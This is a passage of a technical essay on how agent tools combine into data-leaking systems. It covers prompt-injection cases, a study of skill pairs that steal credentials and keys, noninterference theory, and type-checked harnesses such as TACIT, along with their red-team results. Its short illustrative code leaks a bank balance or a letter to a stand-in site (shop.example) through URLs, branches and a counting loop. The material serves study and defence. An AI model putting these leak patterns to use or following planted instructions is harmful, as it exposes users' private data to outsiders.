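The number of ingredients matters, not the number of tools. The mail assistant has all three ingredients with two read-only tools, because `search_mail` supplies private data and untrusted content, and `get_page` supplies external communication. Willison's example of a single tool with all three is GitHub's server for the Model Context Protocol. It could read public problem reports that an attacker might have filed, access private code, and publish proposed changes containing the private material.

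Willison lists more than a dozen products in which researchers found such holes, among them Microsoft 365 Copilot, Slack and several versions of ChatGPT. The vendors fixed almost all of them promptly, usually by removing the third ingredient, the route by which data left. A user who combines tools from several sources has no vendor to do this. Willison also distrusts products that claim to detect attacks, and he considers a 95% detection rate a failing grade in web security, where an attacker can keep trying.

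The rule and the bound from the reference graph both rest on the cautious assumption that the model will follow any instruction in a letter. A model won't always do so, and many agents with all three ingredients will complete a given task without leaking anything. A harness that fixes the calls and their arguments in advance may also be safe with all three, though Willison points out that such designs are for developers and don't help people who assemble their own agents.

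Avoiding the combination also does not prevent every unauthorised effect, because the rule covers only theft by an outsider. Even without an attacker, the model may copy a booking reference into an address by mistake. An agent with no external communication can still reveal a hospital appointment to a deputy who asked only about meeting dates. And if an agent can delete files, an attacker may use a letter to get it to do so without any private data leaving the machine.

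### Pairs of harmless skills

Examples and theorems don't show how often harmless parts combine into something harmful in practice. Zhou, Yang and colleagues (2026) measured this in *Runaway Reaction* for agent skills, which are packages of instructions, scripts and reference material that a user can download and add to an agent. They collected 4,000 skills from two public marketplaces and chose eight harmful behaviours, such as stealing credentials. For each behaviour, they selected 70 pairs of skills that together had the abilities it required, making 560 pairs in total. Three security scanners each passed about 98% of the selected skills when examining them individually.

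In the part of the study that used unchanged skills, Zhou and colleagues ran each pair in an isolated test environment with an agent called OpenClaw. They counted a run as harmful only if the harmful result occurred there, regardless of what the agent wrote in its answer. In one of their examples, one skill loads settings, including passwords and keys, from a local file, and another sends supplied data to a web address. Neither skill is malicious, but together they can send the keys to an outsider.

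The rates depended heavily on the request and on how the researchers had chosen the pairs.

| Request and pairs | Model | Harmful runs |
|---|---|---|
| a request that pointed to the second skill, with matched pairs | DeepSeek-V4-Flash | 27.9% |
| the same | GPT-4o-mini | 9.7% |
| a plain request, with matched pairs | not named | 17.0% |
| a plain request, with random pairs | not named | 3.1% |

In the credentials case, for the first two rows, the user asked the agent to review a settings file and then use the installed sending skill for an external check that reported only whether it passed. The user had therefore asked for a message to leave the machine, but not for it to contain the keys. In the plain request, the user asked only which settings were present and which were missing.

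One behaviour accounts for much of the average for GPT-4o-mini, a small model from 2024. The model stole SSH keys, which give access to remote machines, in 42.9% of runs, but averaged about 5% across the other seven behaviours. DeepSeek-V4-Flash's rates ranged from 15.7% to 38.6%.

These rates don't estimate how often users come to harm, because the researchers selected the matched pairs for a particular harmful result, which ordinary users don't do. The rate for random pairs is nearer to what chance would produce, but even those runs used an environment set up for the harmful behaviour. The contrast between 17.0% and 3.1% is more informative than either number. It fits the idea that harm depends much more on whether the parts complement each other than on how many there are.

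All eight behaviours end by writing, sending or executing something. Three send out credentials, keys or other data, one runs hidden commands, and four alter files, settings or software. Every harmful combination in the study therefore included a part that could do this, so the results are not evidence about combinations of pure tools. The three behaviours that send data are still relevant to read-only tools that contact outsiders. One of them sends the data inside a name lookup, which `get_page` also performs before it fetches a page.

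Zhou and colleagues also give a formal argument close to Spera's, but theirs accounts for the order of the steps. They represent what a set of skills can do as all the ordered sequences of its distinct abilities. The mail assistant's three tools give 15 sequences: 3 of length one, 6 of length two and 6 of length three. A reviewer who examines the tools individually sees only the 3 single steps, so the combination adds 12. A letter could end up in an address only in the 4 of those 12 where `search_mail` comes before `get_page`, assuming each tool runs only once.

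### Authority defined for the whole set

Spera writes that the failure of composition "cannot be patched by better component design". This is true within the model, because the analyst fixes the rules before asking the question. But in practice a developer can replace a component with one that has different abilities. If `get_page` only returns stored copies of approved pages, the assistant loses *u*₂, and the rule for disclosure can't fire.

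Miller and Shapiro's paper centres on programs whose purpose is to limit what other programs can do. They object that formal security researchers had overlooked such programs for thirty years because they treated every program as hostile. The harness or a tool can be such a program. But a developer would have little reason to restrict `get_page` without knowing that the same agent could read private mail. Better components can fix the problem if their designer has considered how the tools will be combined.

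Pure tools need the same attention when other tools are present. Suppose the user adds `unlock`, a program on her own machine that decrypts attachments with a key built into its code. It is pure because the same attachment always gives the same text and nobody outside can observe the call. Before she added it, a stranger who stole an encrypted attachment through `get_page` would have received gibberish. Now the agent can find the attachment, decrypt it and put the text in an address that `get_page` requests. `unlock` supplies one of the three preconditions for this leak, so adding a pure tool has increased what the set can disclose. If all the tools were pure, no tool call could send the text anywhere, and only the harness, a remote model or whatever receives the answer could disclose it.

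The dispute about whether combinations create authority comes down to what one compares the combination with. Write Auth(*X*) for everything that a set of tools *X* can bring about when a given harness and model connect them. Spera compares the whole with its parts:

Auth(*X*) ∪ Auth(*Y*) ⊆ Auth(*X* ∪ *Y*)

The right-hand side can be larger, and in the mail assistant it also includes the power to disclose mail. Capability security compares the authority of the whole system at different times. Once the developer has connected *X* and *Y*, their arrangement limits Auth(*X* ∪ *Y*), and no letter, model output or sequence of calls can raise that limit unless someone adds a connection from outside. Neither of the mail assistant's tools could disclose mail alone, but the connected assistant had that power before the first request. A reviewer has to assess the tools, the harness and the model together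 to find it.

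## Does secrecy survive composition?

The function *f*(*s*) = *s* is pure because its result depends only on its argument and calling it has no side effects. But if *s* is a bank balance, anyone who reads the result learns the balance. Purity therefore doesn't guarantee secrecy, which depends on what an observer can learn. Secrecy doesn't require purity either, because a program that writes the word "done" to a public log after every run has a side effect, yet readers of the log learn nothing about the data it processed.

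The union rule for effects therefore doesn't help with secrecy. Secrecy needs its own definition, and whether it survives composition depends on how the parts are connected.

### Noninterference

Goguen and Meseguer proposed the standard definition in 1982. Their test is to delete the secret activity from a run and ask whether the observer could notice. Suppose Heidi has access to secrets and Lucy does not. Let *cs* be a sequence of commands from both of them, purge(*cs*) the same sequence without Heidi's commands, and seen(*cs*) what Lucy sees. Heidi does not interfere with Lucy if

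seen(*cs*) = seen(purge(*cs*)) for every sequence *cs*

UC Davis' course slides *ECS 235B, Foundations of Computer and Information Security* (2026) apply this to a machine that stores two bits, a high one for Heidi and a low one for Lucy. Each command either flips a bit or leaves it alone. If Heidi's commands affect only the high bit, Lucy sees the same thing with or without them, so the property holds. It fails if they also affect the low bit, because Lucy can then notice them.

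For functions, the definition compares inputs instead of commands. Label every part of the input and output as secret or public, and write *x* ~ *y* if *x* and *y* have the same public parts. Their secret parts may differ. A deterministic function *f* respects the labels if

*x* ~ *y* implies *f*(*x*) ~ *f*(*y*)

In words, changing the secret inputs does not change the public outputs. The function *f*(*s*) = *s* respects the labels if its output is labelled secret and violates them if it is labelled public. `summarise` respects them if the summary of a private letter is also labelled private.

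The definition covers two ways in which a secret can reach an output. In an **explicit flow**, the program copies the secret or computes something from it, as when it adds the user's balance to a web address. In an **implicit flow**, the secret determines which instructions run:

```
if balance > 1000:
    get_page("https://shop.example/offers")
```

The shop learns from the request that the balance is above 1,000, even though the address contains no part of the balance. If the shop was expecting a request, it also learns something when none arrives.

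A harness could try to catch such flows by labelling as secret anything that the program changes inside a branch that depends on a secret. That isn't enough, because a branch that doesn't run can also leak:

```
tmp  = True
rich = True
if balance > 1000: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: get_page("https://shop.example/offers")
```

If the balance is above 1,000, the program sets `tmp` to false and the harness labels it secret. The next line does nothing, so `rich` stays true and public. If the balance is lower, `tmp` stays true and public, so the program sets `rich` to false and the harness doesn't label it secret. Either way, `rich` is labelled public but reveals whether the balance is above 1,000. Garby and colleagues trace the example to work by Fenton in the 1970s and found the same gap in CaMeL's label tracking.

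A common remedy is to stop the program when it tries to change a public variable inside a secret branch. Here it would stop at `tmp = False`. But the program then stops if the balance is above 1,000 and finishes otherwise, so an observer who can see whether it stopped still learns one bit about the balance.

### Running two functions in sequence

Suppose that *f* and *g* are deterministic, always finish and respect the labels, and that *g* accepts *f*'s outputs with the labels *f* gave them. Then

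*x* ~ *y* ⇒ *f*(*x*) ~ *f*(*y*) ⇒ *g*(*f*(*x*)) ~ *g*(*f*(*y*))

The first step holds because *f* respects the labels, and the second because *g* does. The sequence therefore respects them, and the same argument extends to sequences of any length. An observer who also sees the public part of the intermediate result learns nothing extra, because that part is the same for *x* and *y*.

The proof applies only if every tool respects the same labels. `get_page` reveals its argument to a website, so it must refuse any address labelled secret. If `summarise` labels its output secret and `get_page` ignores the label, the letter can leak.

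With labels in force, the mail assistant can't complete its original task. The hotel's address comes from a booking confirmation in a private mailbox, so the address is labelled secret and `get_page` rejects it. Somebody has to authorise releasing the address, a step called declassification. Noninterference describes a workflow that releases no secrets, so every useful exception needs a separate justification.

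### McCullough's counterexample

The proof also assumes that the same input always gives the same output. This isn't true of a model that samples its replies, or of many ordinary systems whose behaviour depends on scheduling. For such systems, secrecy has to be defined in terms of which outputs are possible. **Generalized noninterference** requires that anything a public observer might see is compatible with every possible series of secret inputs.

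McCullough examined whether secrecy properties survive composition in *Specifications for Multi-Level Security and a Hook-Up Property* (1987) and *Noninterference and the composability of security properties* (1988). He found a pair of systems that are each secure but leak when connected. McLean's *A General Theory of Composition for Trace Sets* (1994) describes the example in detail.

System A receives secret messages, works on each one for a while and sends it out on a secret channel. A public user can send A the command *cancel*, which A eventually passes on. If A has no unfinished message when it passes the command on, it may also publish the note "nothing to cancel", but it doesn't have to. System B works the same way, except that it doesn't pass *cancel* on, and it checks for unfinished messages when the command arrives.

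Each system is secure alone. If a reader sees a note from A, there may have been no secret messages, or A may have finished handling them all. If the reader sees no note, A may have been busy, or it may have been idle and published nothing. Every observation is compatible with any series of secret messages.

When the two systems are connected, A sends its secret messages to B, B sends its own back to A, and A passes *cancel* to B. Once a secret message enters A, it circulates between the two systems forever. If transfers take no time, the message is always in exactly one of them, so when *cancel* passes from A to B, one system is busy and can't publish a note. A reader who sees notes from both systems therefore knows that no secret message ever entered.

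McLean works out the probabilities, assuming that an idle system publishes a note half the time and that a circulating message is equally likely to be in either system.

| What the reader sees | Without a secret message | With a secret message |
|---|---|---|
| no note | 25% | 50% |
| a note from A only | 25% | 25% |
| a note from B only | 25% | 25% |
| notes from both | 25% | 0% |

A malicious program with access to the secret channel can use this to signal. It sends a 1 by submitting a message and a 0 by blocking all messages. With these percentages, each use leaks at most ½ log₂(5/4) ≈ 0.16 bits (McLean gives about 0.17), so leaking a 16-bit bank balance takes about 100 uses.

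A slow component can leak by itself. The malicious program can flood it with messages, so it is idle less often and publishes fewer notes. Generalized noninterference doesn't rule this out, because it restricts only which outputs are possible, not how likely they are. If each component clears its messages faster than the program can submit them, its notes appear half the time whatever the program does, and it leaks nothing by itself. But as McLean points out, connecting two such components still creates a leak.

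McCullough identifies feedback as the cause. Generalized noninterference still holds in a cascade, where A sends data to B and B sends nothing back. Zakinthinos and Lee (1995) proved McCullough's conjecture that noninterference composes without feedback, and found a way to connect systems with feedback while preserving it.

Feedback causes trouble because these properties require certain runs to be possible. The composite is secure only if some run has a secret message and notes from both systems. A and B can each produce their half of such a run, but no two halves fit together so that each system receives exactly what the other sends.

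### Properties that survive feedback

McCullough proposed a stronger property, **restrictiveness**. *Formal approaches to information hiding* (2011) summarises it as requiring that no secret information affect the system's behaviour as a public user sees it. *A hookup theorem for multilevel security* (McCullough, 1990) shows that any collection of restrictive systems forms a restrictive whole. Other researchers later found more properties that compose. The table gives results from McLean and from Mantel's *On the Composition of Secure Systems* (2002) for connecting systems that all have the same property.

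| Property | What it requires | Survives a cascade | Survives feedback |
|---|---|---|---|
| generalized noninterference | any public behaviour is compatible with any secret inputs | yes | not always |
| noninference (a different property from noninterference) | every run is still possible after deleting all its secret events | yes | yes |
| separability | any secret history is compatible with any public history | yes | yes |
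| restrictiveness | secrets never affect behaviour as a public user sees it | yes | yes |
| forward correctability | generalized noninterference, plus a condition on secret inputs just before public ones | yes | yes |

System B is flawed because it fails the extra condition in forward correctability. Take a run in which B receives *cancel* and publishes a note, and insert a secret message just before *cancel*. Generalized noninterference lets us repair the run by having B finish the message before *cancel* arrives. Forward correctability allows changes only after the public input, here *cancel*. By then B has received the command while busy, so it cannot publish the note.

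Mantel shows that a weaker version of forward correctability also composes. It drops the requirement about deleting a secret input and keeps a limited form of the requirement about inserting one. This refuted an earlier claim that forward correctability was the weakest property of its kind that composes.

A property that survives composition can still be too weak or too strict to use. McLean considers noninference too weak in general, since adding secret input may still influence public output. Separability is strong and simple, but it suits only systems where public events don't affect secret ones. It would rule out an ordinary use of the mail assistant, where text from a public web page changes the private answer to the user.

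Mantel's results also reduce the number of components that need checking. A component that never handles secrets satisfies all the basic conditions from which he builds these properties. So does a component that produces nothing a public observer can see, although for some conditions it must also accept any input at any time. If the observer is a website, a local `summarise` from an untrusted author may therefore need no proof. Components that both handle secrets and produce public events do need one. In the mail assistant, this is the combination of model, harness and `get_page`.

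### Feedback in the agent loop

An agent loop shares several features with McCullough's example. Data flows in both directions between the model and the tools, and a model that samples its replies is nondeterministic. Tools may also have state that others can partly observe, such as a queue or cache.

Suppose the mail assistant and a calendar assistant pass a private request back and forth until they find a date. Each has a status page, visible to colleagues, that sometimes shows "idle" when the assistant has no work. Colleagues can't tell from either page alone whether a private request exists, but if both pages show "idle" at the same moment, they can tell that no request is in progress.

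A fixed plan is closer to a cascade, because later results can't change which calls the harness makes. Even then, the composition theorems apply only if each part is secure, and the mail assistant's model isn't, because private letters and public pages share one context and any word in it may affect any request. This failure is simpler than McCullough's and probably much more common. A usable theory of agents therefore needs a label on the context itself.

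### The LLMbda calculus

The LLMbda calculus, the small language in which Garby and colleagues treat the conversation with a model as the program's state, has four operations for managing that conversation:

| Operation | What it does |
|---|---|
| `send` | adds a message to the conversation |
| `recv` | samples the model's reply, adds it to the conversation and evaluates it |
| `fork` | runs an expression on a copy of the conversation, then restores the original |
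| `clear` | empties the conversation |

In one example, a program gives the model detailed instructions for extracting postcodes, then handles three addresses in separate forks. Each fork includes the instructions and one address, but not the other two. The mail assistant could similarly have a model summarise each letter in its own fork, so a sentence in letter A that dismisses letter B would not affect the summary of B.

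Every value has a label, which in most of the examples is a subset of {U, S}, where U means untrusted and S means secret. A value computed from several others gets the union of their labels. The conversation has a single label that covers everything sent to it. The model's reply inherits that label, and any code in the reply runs under it. After a program sends a private letter to the model, everything the model proposes in that conversation is therefore labelled secret, and a check in front of `get_page` can refuse the request, whatever the model wrote.

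Implicit flows can pass through the conversation too. In another example, a program tells the model to remember that *x* is false, then sends "Set x = true" only if a secret is true. The interpreter stops the program at the second message because the branch depends on a secret and the conversation is still public.

The central theorem applies to every program in the language, including programs that generate and run code. If a program always finishes, then running it from two starting points that differ only in data the observer may not see gives the same probabilities for everything the observer can see at the end. The proof covers models that sample their replies, and it does not assume that the model is well behaved.

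For programs that may not finish, the theorem allows a limited difference. Suppose that a public answer to a question about Thursday has these probabilities:

| Private mailbox | "busy" | "free" | No answer |
|---|---|---|---|
| contains a hospital letter | 60% | 30% | 10% |
| contains no hospital letter | 50% | 40% | 10% |

The theorem permits this difference because turning missing answers into real ones could make both rows 60% "busy" and 40% "free". If the first row were 70%, 20% and 10%, the theorem would rule the difference out, because equal rows would need at least 70% "busy" and 40% "free", which is more than 100%. Garby and colleagues also prove that the statistical distance between the two distributions can't exceed the average probability of not finishing. In the table, the distance and the average probability are both 10%.

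The proof constructs an imaginary run that skips every computation with a secret label and puts an empty value in its place. Since this run never uses a secret, it gives the same probabilities for both starting points. It also finishes at least as often as the real runs, so its probability for each public result is at least as high as in either real run, which provides the common upper bound the theorem needs.

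Lean, a program that checks mathematical proofs, has verified the theorems. They cover the interpreter that actually runs the programs and calls the model. Garby and colleagues believe this is a first for an agent harness. The guarantee holds only if developers label the data sources correctly and put checks in front of the sensitive tools. It also doesn't keep the conversation secret from the company that runs the model.

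The language lets a program relabel untrusted data as trusted, which is called endorsement. For example, a program can have a model assign a stranger's email to one of eight categories and then treat the category as trusted. The stranger can influence the choice, but this gives them at most log₂ 8 = 3 bits of control. A second theorem shows that even careless endorsement can't weaken the protection of secrets.

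Garby and colleagues tested whether programs under these rules are still useful by building an agent called Randori and running it on AgentDojo's banking tasks with three models. Attacks succeeded in 2 of 1,296 runs. That figure overstates the labels' effect, because about two-thirds of the combinations of task and attack needed an action that the agent's plan would never include, so the labels mattered only in the other 423 runs. In both successful attacks, the user had asked the agent to pay according to a file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. Forbidding endorsement blocked this attack, but when there was no attack, it also reduced the number of tasks completed from 36 to 30 of 48 with one model and from 31 to 26 with another.

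### Leaks through termination and timing

The main theorem is **termination-insensitive**, meaning that a secret may influence whether the program finishes. If the observer sees only the final result, a deterministic program can leak at most one bit per run this way, but repeated runs can leak the whole secret. A program that stops whenever a chosen bit of the balance is 1 reveals that bit, so 16 runs, each testing a different bit, reveal a 16-bit balance. Garby and colleagues found such a channel in CaMeL, which retries failed programs in an ordinary Python loop that the label tracking does not cover.

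Randori's retry loop runs inside the calculus. The agent first practises on artificial data and gets the real data only once its program works, so errors during practice can't depend on the user's secrets. But if another program runs the whole agent repeatedly and records which runs fail, those failures can again leak information about the secrets.

A single run can leak much more than one bit if the observer sees output before the program stops. Askarov, Hunt, Sabelfeld and Sands made this point in the title of a 2008 paper, *Termination-insensitive noninterference leaks more than just a bit*. The following program shows how it can happen:

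```
for i in 0, 1, 2, ...:
    get_page("https://shop.example/" + i)
    if i == balance: loop forever
```

Each address contains only a public counter, but the requests stop when the counter reaches the balance, so the shop can read the balance from the last request. A 16-bit balance takes at most 65,536 requests, but the method is infeasible for an encryption key because it could take up to 2¹²⁸.

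The LLMbda theorem compares final states. In their evaluation, Garby and colleagues use tools that operate on a simulated world inside the program, and they acknowledge that a better model would include interaction with outside data and tools. In a live assistant, a request to a website can't be undone when the program later stalls, so the theorem would have to cover requests as they happen.

Time is another output that the definition omits. Suppose the assistant fetches a public page, summarises all the user's hospital letters, and then fetches another page from the same website. If each summary takes two seconds, the website's operator can estimate the number of letters from the interval between the requests. To prevent this leak, the definition would have to treat the time of each request as public output, and the harness would have to send requests on a schedule that doesn't depend on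 the mailbox.

### Harmless answers that identify someone

Suppose the mail assistant works for a company's personnel office, and a manager may ask it general questions. One employee has written to request medical leave. The manager asks which department the employee works in, and the assistant answers "Legal", which has 12 employees. Later, the manager asks what year the employee joined, and the assistant answers 2019, when 40 people joined. Each answer alone leaves at least 12 candidates, but if only one person in Legal joined in 2019, the two answers together identify the employee.

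This is called aggregation, and it doesn't show that noninterference fails to compose. If two deterministic functions each return a public result that doesn't depend on the secret, the pair of results doesn't depend on it either. In the example, each answer already depended on the secret letter. Someone had judged each disclosure small enough to allow, but that judgement didn't cover the two together.

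Two random outputs can reveal a secret together even if neither does alone. Suppose one tool returns a random key *k*, and another returns the secret *s* encrypted by flipping the bits where *k* has a 1. If *s* is 0110 and *k* is 1011, the second tool returns 1101. Either output alone is a uniformly random string, whatever the secret is, but anyone with both can recover *s* exactly. Checking each tool's output probabilities separately wouldn't reveal the problem, because the tools share a key.

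*Information Flow Type Systems* (Jia, 2025) gives a larger-scale example of aggregation, the heatmap published by the fitness app Strava. People may not mind sharing anonymised exercise data, but data recorded at a sensitive location can reveal something about the place. Jia attributes the problem to security properties that don't handle declassification well. Each user's consent covers only their own data, not what the combined map shows about the location.

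Asking for confirmation before each release doesn't solve this. *PerMIT* (Jiang, Bai and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent memory in which untrusted content can affect the agent only through a gate that displays it for confirmation. The paper proves noninterference relative to that display, meaning that the agent behaves the same in any two runs with the same user input, randomness, schedule and display, whatever the hidden content. Each confirmation authorises one exact value for one tool. It doesn't cover the purpose or the other arguments, and the agent may reuse the value later without asking. If the same kind of gate controlled the personnel assistant's answers, someone could approve "Legal" on Monday and "2019" on Tuesday without seeing the two together.

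### Differential privacy

For statistics about many people, there is a guarantee that does account for repeated releases. **Differential privacy** adds random noise to each answer so that no single person's record affects it much. Formally, a query *M* is ε-differentially private if, for any two data sets *D* and *D′* that differ in one person's record and any set *S* of possible answers,

Pr[*M*(*D*) ∈ *S*] ≤ e<sup>ε</sup> · Pr[*M*(*D′*) ∈ *S*]

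A smaller ε gives stronger protection. At ε = 0, the answers would not depend on the records. This satisfies noninterference but makes the query useless.

If two queries use independent noise, the probability of a pair of answers is the product of the separate probabilities. The bounds therefore multiply:

e<sup>ε₁</sup> · e<sup>ε₂</sup> = e<sup>ε₁ + ε₂</sup>

The values of ε add up. They still add up if an agent chooses each query after reading the previous answers, because the bound for each query holds whatever those answers were. Unlike generalized noninterference, the guarantee therefore still holds under feedback.

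The total can grow quickly. One query at ε = 0.1 allows a probability ratio of at most e<sup>0.1</sup> ≈ 1.1. Fifty queries give a total of ε = 5, which raises the bound to e<sup>5</sup> ≈ 148. Suppose an observer initially thinks there is a 1% chance that a particular employee has requested medical leave. After one answer, that estimate can rise to at most 1.1%, but after 50 it can reach 60%.

These worst-case figures hold for any set of 50 queries. A sharper theorem lowers the total from 5 to about 3.9, and the ratio to about 50, if the designer accepts adding a probability of one in 100,000 to the bound.

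Repeating a query weakens privacy because averaging the answers removes much of the noise. A common method for a count at ε = 0.1 adds noise with a standard deviation of about 14. If the manager asks how many employees requested medical leave and gets fresh noise each time, the average of 50 answers has an error of about 2. A harness can prevent this by returning the stored answer when someone repeats a question, but it may not detect that a reworded question is the same. It therefore has to add up the ε of every query and refuse new ones once the total reaches a limit. Tools that read the same records need a shared total, because two tools each limited to ε = 1 can reach 2 together.

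The method suits the personnel office, where an error of 14 may be acceptable in a count of several hundred, but not the original mail assistant. A user who asks when she can check in at her hotel needs an exact fact from one letter, and enough noise to hide that letter would make the answer useless.

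## Can a workflow be checked before it runs?

It is better to find flaws before a workflow runs, because some effects can't be undone. Once `get_page` has requested an address containing the user's bank balance, the balance is in a stranger's log. A compiler can often find such flaws in an ordinary program by examining its code. An agent's workflow usually has no code to examine in advance, because the model chooses each call after seeing the result of the last one.

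A harness can make the model write a program and check the program's types before running it. An analyst can describe the tools in a formal model and search it for harmful sequences of calls. A tester can run the agent on hostile input and observe what it does.

### Checking the types of the agent's program

Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, describe a harness called TACIT that takes the first approach. It uses Scala 3's capture sets, which record the capabilities a function can use. A request goes through these steps:

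1. The model writes a short Scala program and sends it as the argument of a tool call.
2. The compiler checks the program with capture checking turned on. It also applies a "safe mode" that forbids type casts, reflection and other ways of hiding a capability from the compiler. If the check fails, nothing runs, and the model can use the error messages to try again.
3. If the check succeeds, the program runs in a local Scala session. It can reach files, the network and other programs only through a library of capabilities.
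4. The library returns sensitive data, such as the text of a letter, in a wrapper called `Classified`.
5. Ordinary results go back to the model. When the program prints a wrapped value, the user sees the contents on her screen, but the model receives only `Classified(****)`.

The agent has no method for taking the contents out of the wrapper. It can only call `map`, which applies a function to the contents and wraps the result again:

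`def map[U](f: T -> U): Classified[U]`

The plain arrow means that `f` can't capture any capability, so it can't write a file, contact a website or print. Only the code that handles secrets has to be free of side effects. Odersky and colleagues call this local purity.

In this system, the mail assistant's tools could have the following types, where `using Network` means that a call needs the network capability:

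```
def search_mail(query: String): Classified[List[Letter]]
def summarise(text: String): String
def get_page(address: String)(using Network): String
```

The compiler accepts this program:

```
val letters = search_mail("hotel booking")
val summary = letters.map { found =>
  summarise(found.map(_.text).mkString("\n"))
}
println(summary)
```

The function passed to `letters.map` joins the letters into one text and summarises it, which requires no capability. The user can read the summary, but the model that wrote the program can't.

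The compiler rejects this one:

```
requestNetwork(Set("shop.example")) {
  letters.map { found =>
    get_page("https://shop.example/?q=" + found.head.text)
  }
}
```

The first line gives the program access to one website, and the function inside `letters.map` uses that access to send a letter there. The function therefore has the type `List[Letter] ->{net} String`, where `net` is the network capability. `map` requires `List[Letter] -> String`, so the type checker rejects the program before it runs, and the shop receives nothing.

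A program also can't leak wrapped data through an implicit flow, such as contacting the shop only if a certain letter exists, because code outside the wrapper can't read the condition. If the program adds the wrapper itself to a web address, the address will contain only the text `Classified(****)`.

The model never reads the letters, so a stranger can't use one to instruct it to make particular calls. Pages fetched with `get_page` aren't wrapped in this example, so they can still mislead the model, but any program it writes in response has to pass the same check.

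The original hotel request fails, as it does under noninterference, because the hotel's address is in a private letter. The program can show the user the address, and she can then in effect declassify it by typing it into her next message.

### What the type check takes on trust

If the compiler accepts a program, no function passed to `map` can send the secret anywhere through a tracked capability. This holds for every letter the mailbox might contain, even if an attacker controls the model. But this guarantee depends on several things the compiler doesn't check.

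- **The labels.** Somebody has to wrap the right data. If the developer had given `search_mail` the result type `List[Letter]`, the compiler would have accepted a program that sends letters to the shop.
- **The library.** The reusable part is about 1,000 lines of Scala. Programmers can exempt a module from safe mode by marking it `@assumeSafe`, but then they have to verify its safety themselves.
- **The compiler.** Capture checking has machine-checked proofs for its core type system. Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that safe mode still needs a further proof that it delivers what they claim for it.
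- **The local model.** A program can send wrapped text to a second model, which the user trusts, and receive a wrapped answer. The types treat this call as pure, which is accurate only if the service keeps nothing between calls. A hostile letter can also still cause this model to write a misleading summary.
- **The user's screen.** If the window that displays the summary fetches images automatically, a hostile letter can leak data through an image address, as in an ordinary chat window.

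TACIT also leaves some checks until the program runs. The library rejects file paths outside the directory the program requested. It catches exceptions, which could otherwise carry secret text out of a function.

Odersky and colleagues list timing and termination among the gaps. A function inside `map` can take longer if a letter mentions a hospital, and the model may be able to detect the delay. They describe this as a one-bit leak, though repeated runs can leak more.

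The compiler also can't track what an external command such as `git` does, because the command runs outside Scala. If the user allows such commands, the check can guarantee only that the agent runs the ones on a permitted list, so Odersky and colleagues recommend adding a sandbox where security is critical. Their check also isn't meant to prevent wrong answers, so a program can pass it and still summarise the wrong letters.

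### How TACIT performed

To test the wrapper, Odersky and colleagues gave agents a software project with a directory of secrets, including API keys and confidential documents. They combined 12 ordinary tasks with 10 sets of planted instructions, for 120 trials. In another 11 trials, the user asked for the secrets, either directly or under a false pretext such as an emergency. They ran all 131 trials with each of two models, once with the secrets wrapped and once with them as plain text. A trial counted as secure if no secret appeared in the agent's output.

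| Model and trials | Secure with the wrapper | Secure without it |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, planted instructions (120) | 100% | 100% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, malicious requests (11) | 100% | 81.8% |
| **Claude Sonnet 4.6, all (131)** | **100%** | **98.5%** |
| MiniMax M2.5, planted instructions (120) | 100% | 97.5% |
| MiniMax M2.5, malicious requests (11) | 100% | 27.3% |
| **MiniMax M2.5, all (131)** | **100%** | **91.6%** |

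Without the wrapper, Sonnet revealed secrets in 2 trials and MiniMax in 11. The perfect scores with the wrapper would be weak evidence by themselves, since a system that leaks in 1% of trials has about a 27% chance of completing 131 trials without a leak. The case for the wrapper depends on the type argument, and in the trials the implementation behaved as that argument predicts.

The agents could still do ordinary tasks with the wrapper. Sonnet completed 99.2% of them with it and 83.3% without it, while MiniMax completed 90.0% with it and 88.3% without it. Sonnet's lower score without the wrapper may be an artefact, because in those runs it often exceeded its limit on turns or time, and sometimes stopped to warn the user about planted instructions.

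Odersky and colleagues also ran TACIT on AgentDojo, using the two models from CaMeL's evaluation. In 1,926 trials, one attack succeeded. A planted review recommended hotel B, and the agent correctly booked hotel A but quoted the review to the user. Under AgentDojo's scoring, this counted as a successful attack because hotel B's name appeared in the answer, although no secret leaked.

They describe the number of tasks completed as comparable to CaMeL's, but with o4-mini-high, TACIT completed far fewer of the office tasks (52.9% versus 81.4%) and chat tasks (47.6% versus 68.6%). With Gemini 2.5 Pro, the two systems were closer, except in travel, where TACIT completed 64.3% of the tasks and CaMeL 1.4%.

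It is also unclear how strictly these runs applied the purity rule. The agent's instructions include a warning that any side effect inside a function passed to `map` happens immediately, but under the rule such a function can't have any. The AgentDojo runs may therefore have tested a slightly different guarantee from the 131 trials.

Another experiment tested whether agents do worse when they have to write typed Scala. The first two columns give results on τ²-bench, a set of simulated customer-service conversations, averaged over 10 runs per task. The last column gives the share of software problems agents solved in SWE-bench Lite. Each cell lists the result for ordinary tool calling first and for TACIT second.

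| Model | Airline | Retail | SWE-bench Lite |
|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8% → 45.2% | 53.3% → 57.0% | not tested |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4% → 61.0% | 75.1% → 77.5% | 43.3% → 41.7% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8% → 58.6% | 74.6% → 75.5% | not tested |

The agents did slightly better at customer service and slightly worse at fixing software. In the customer-service runs, fewer than 8% of the programs needed a second attempt because of a compiler error. The functions in those runs return unwrapped records, so the comparison measures the effect of writing Scala, not of hiding data from the model. The AgentDojo results suggest that hiding data may reduce performance more.

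### Checking code that does not exist yet

TACIT checks one program at a time, and a long task may need many. Zhao, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *LACUNA*, a paper by an overlapping team, put the model's contribution inside a larger program. Where the developer doesn't know in advance what code will be needed, she writes a placeholder with a type:

`val time: String = agent("find the check-in time")`

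When the program reaches this line, the model writes code to replace the placeholder. The compiler checks that code as if the developer had typed it there, and the code runs only if its result would have type `String`. The new code may contain further placeholders, so the model can build a long task in pieces.

The compiler accepts or rejects each snippet as a whole. In one of Zhao and colleagues' examples, the model writes code that subtracts 50 from an account balance and then returns text where the program needs a number. The compiler rejects the code, so the subtraction never runs and the balance stays at 100. In a language that catches such errors only at runtime, the subtraction would already have happened. Similarly, in the mail assistant, a type error on the last line of a snippet prevents a `get_page` request on the first line. The check doesn't help if a snippet compiles and then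 fails halfway through for another reason, such as a website that doesn't respond.

With capture checking and safe mode on, a reviewer can also limit code that the model hasn't written yet. That code can use only the variables and capabilities available at the placeholder. If the network capability isn't among them, the code can't contact a website.

LACUNA also makes the `Classified` wrapper more flexible. In TACIT, the model has to write the function for `map` without seeing the letters. In LACUNA, that function can contain a placeholder for a trusted local model, which reads the letters and writes code to suit them. The compiler checks the new code at the placeholder, where only pure code is allowed, so the local model can adapt to a letter but can't send it anywhere.

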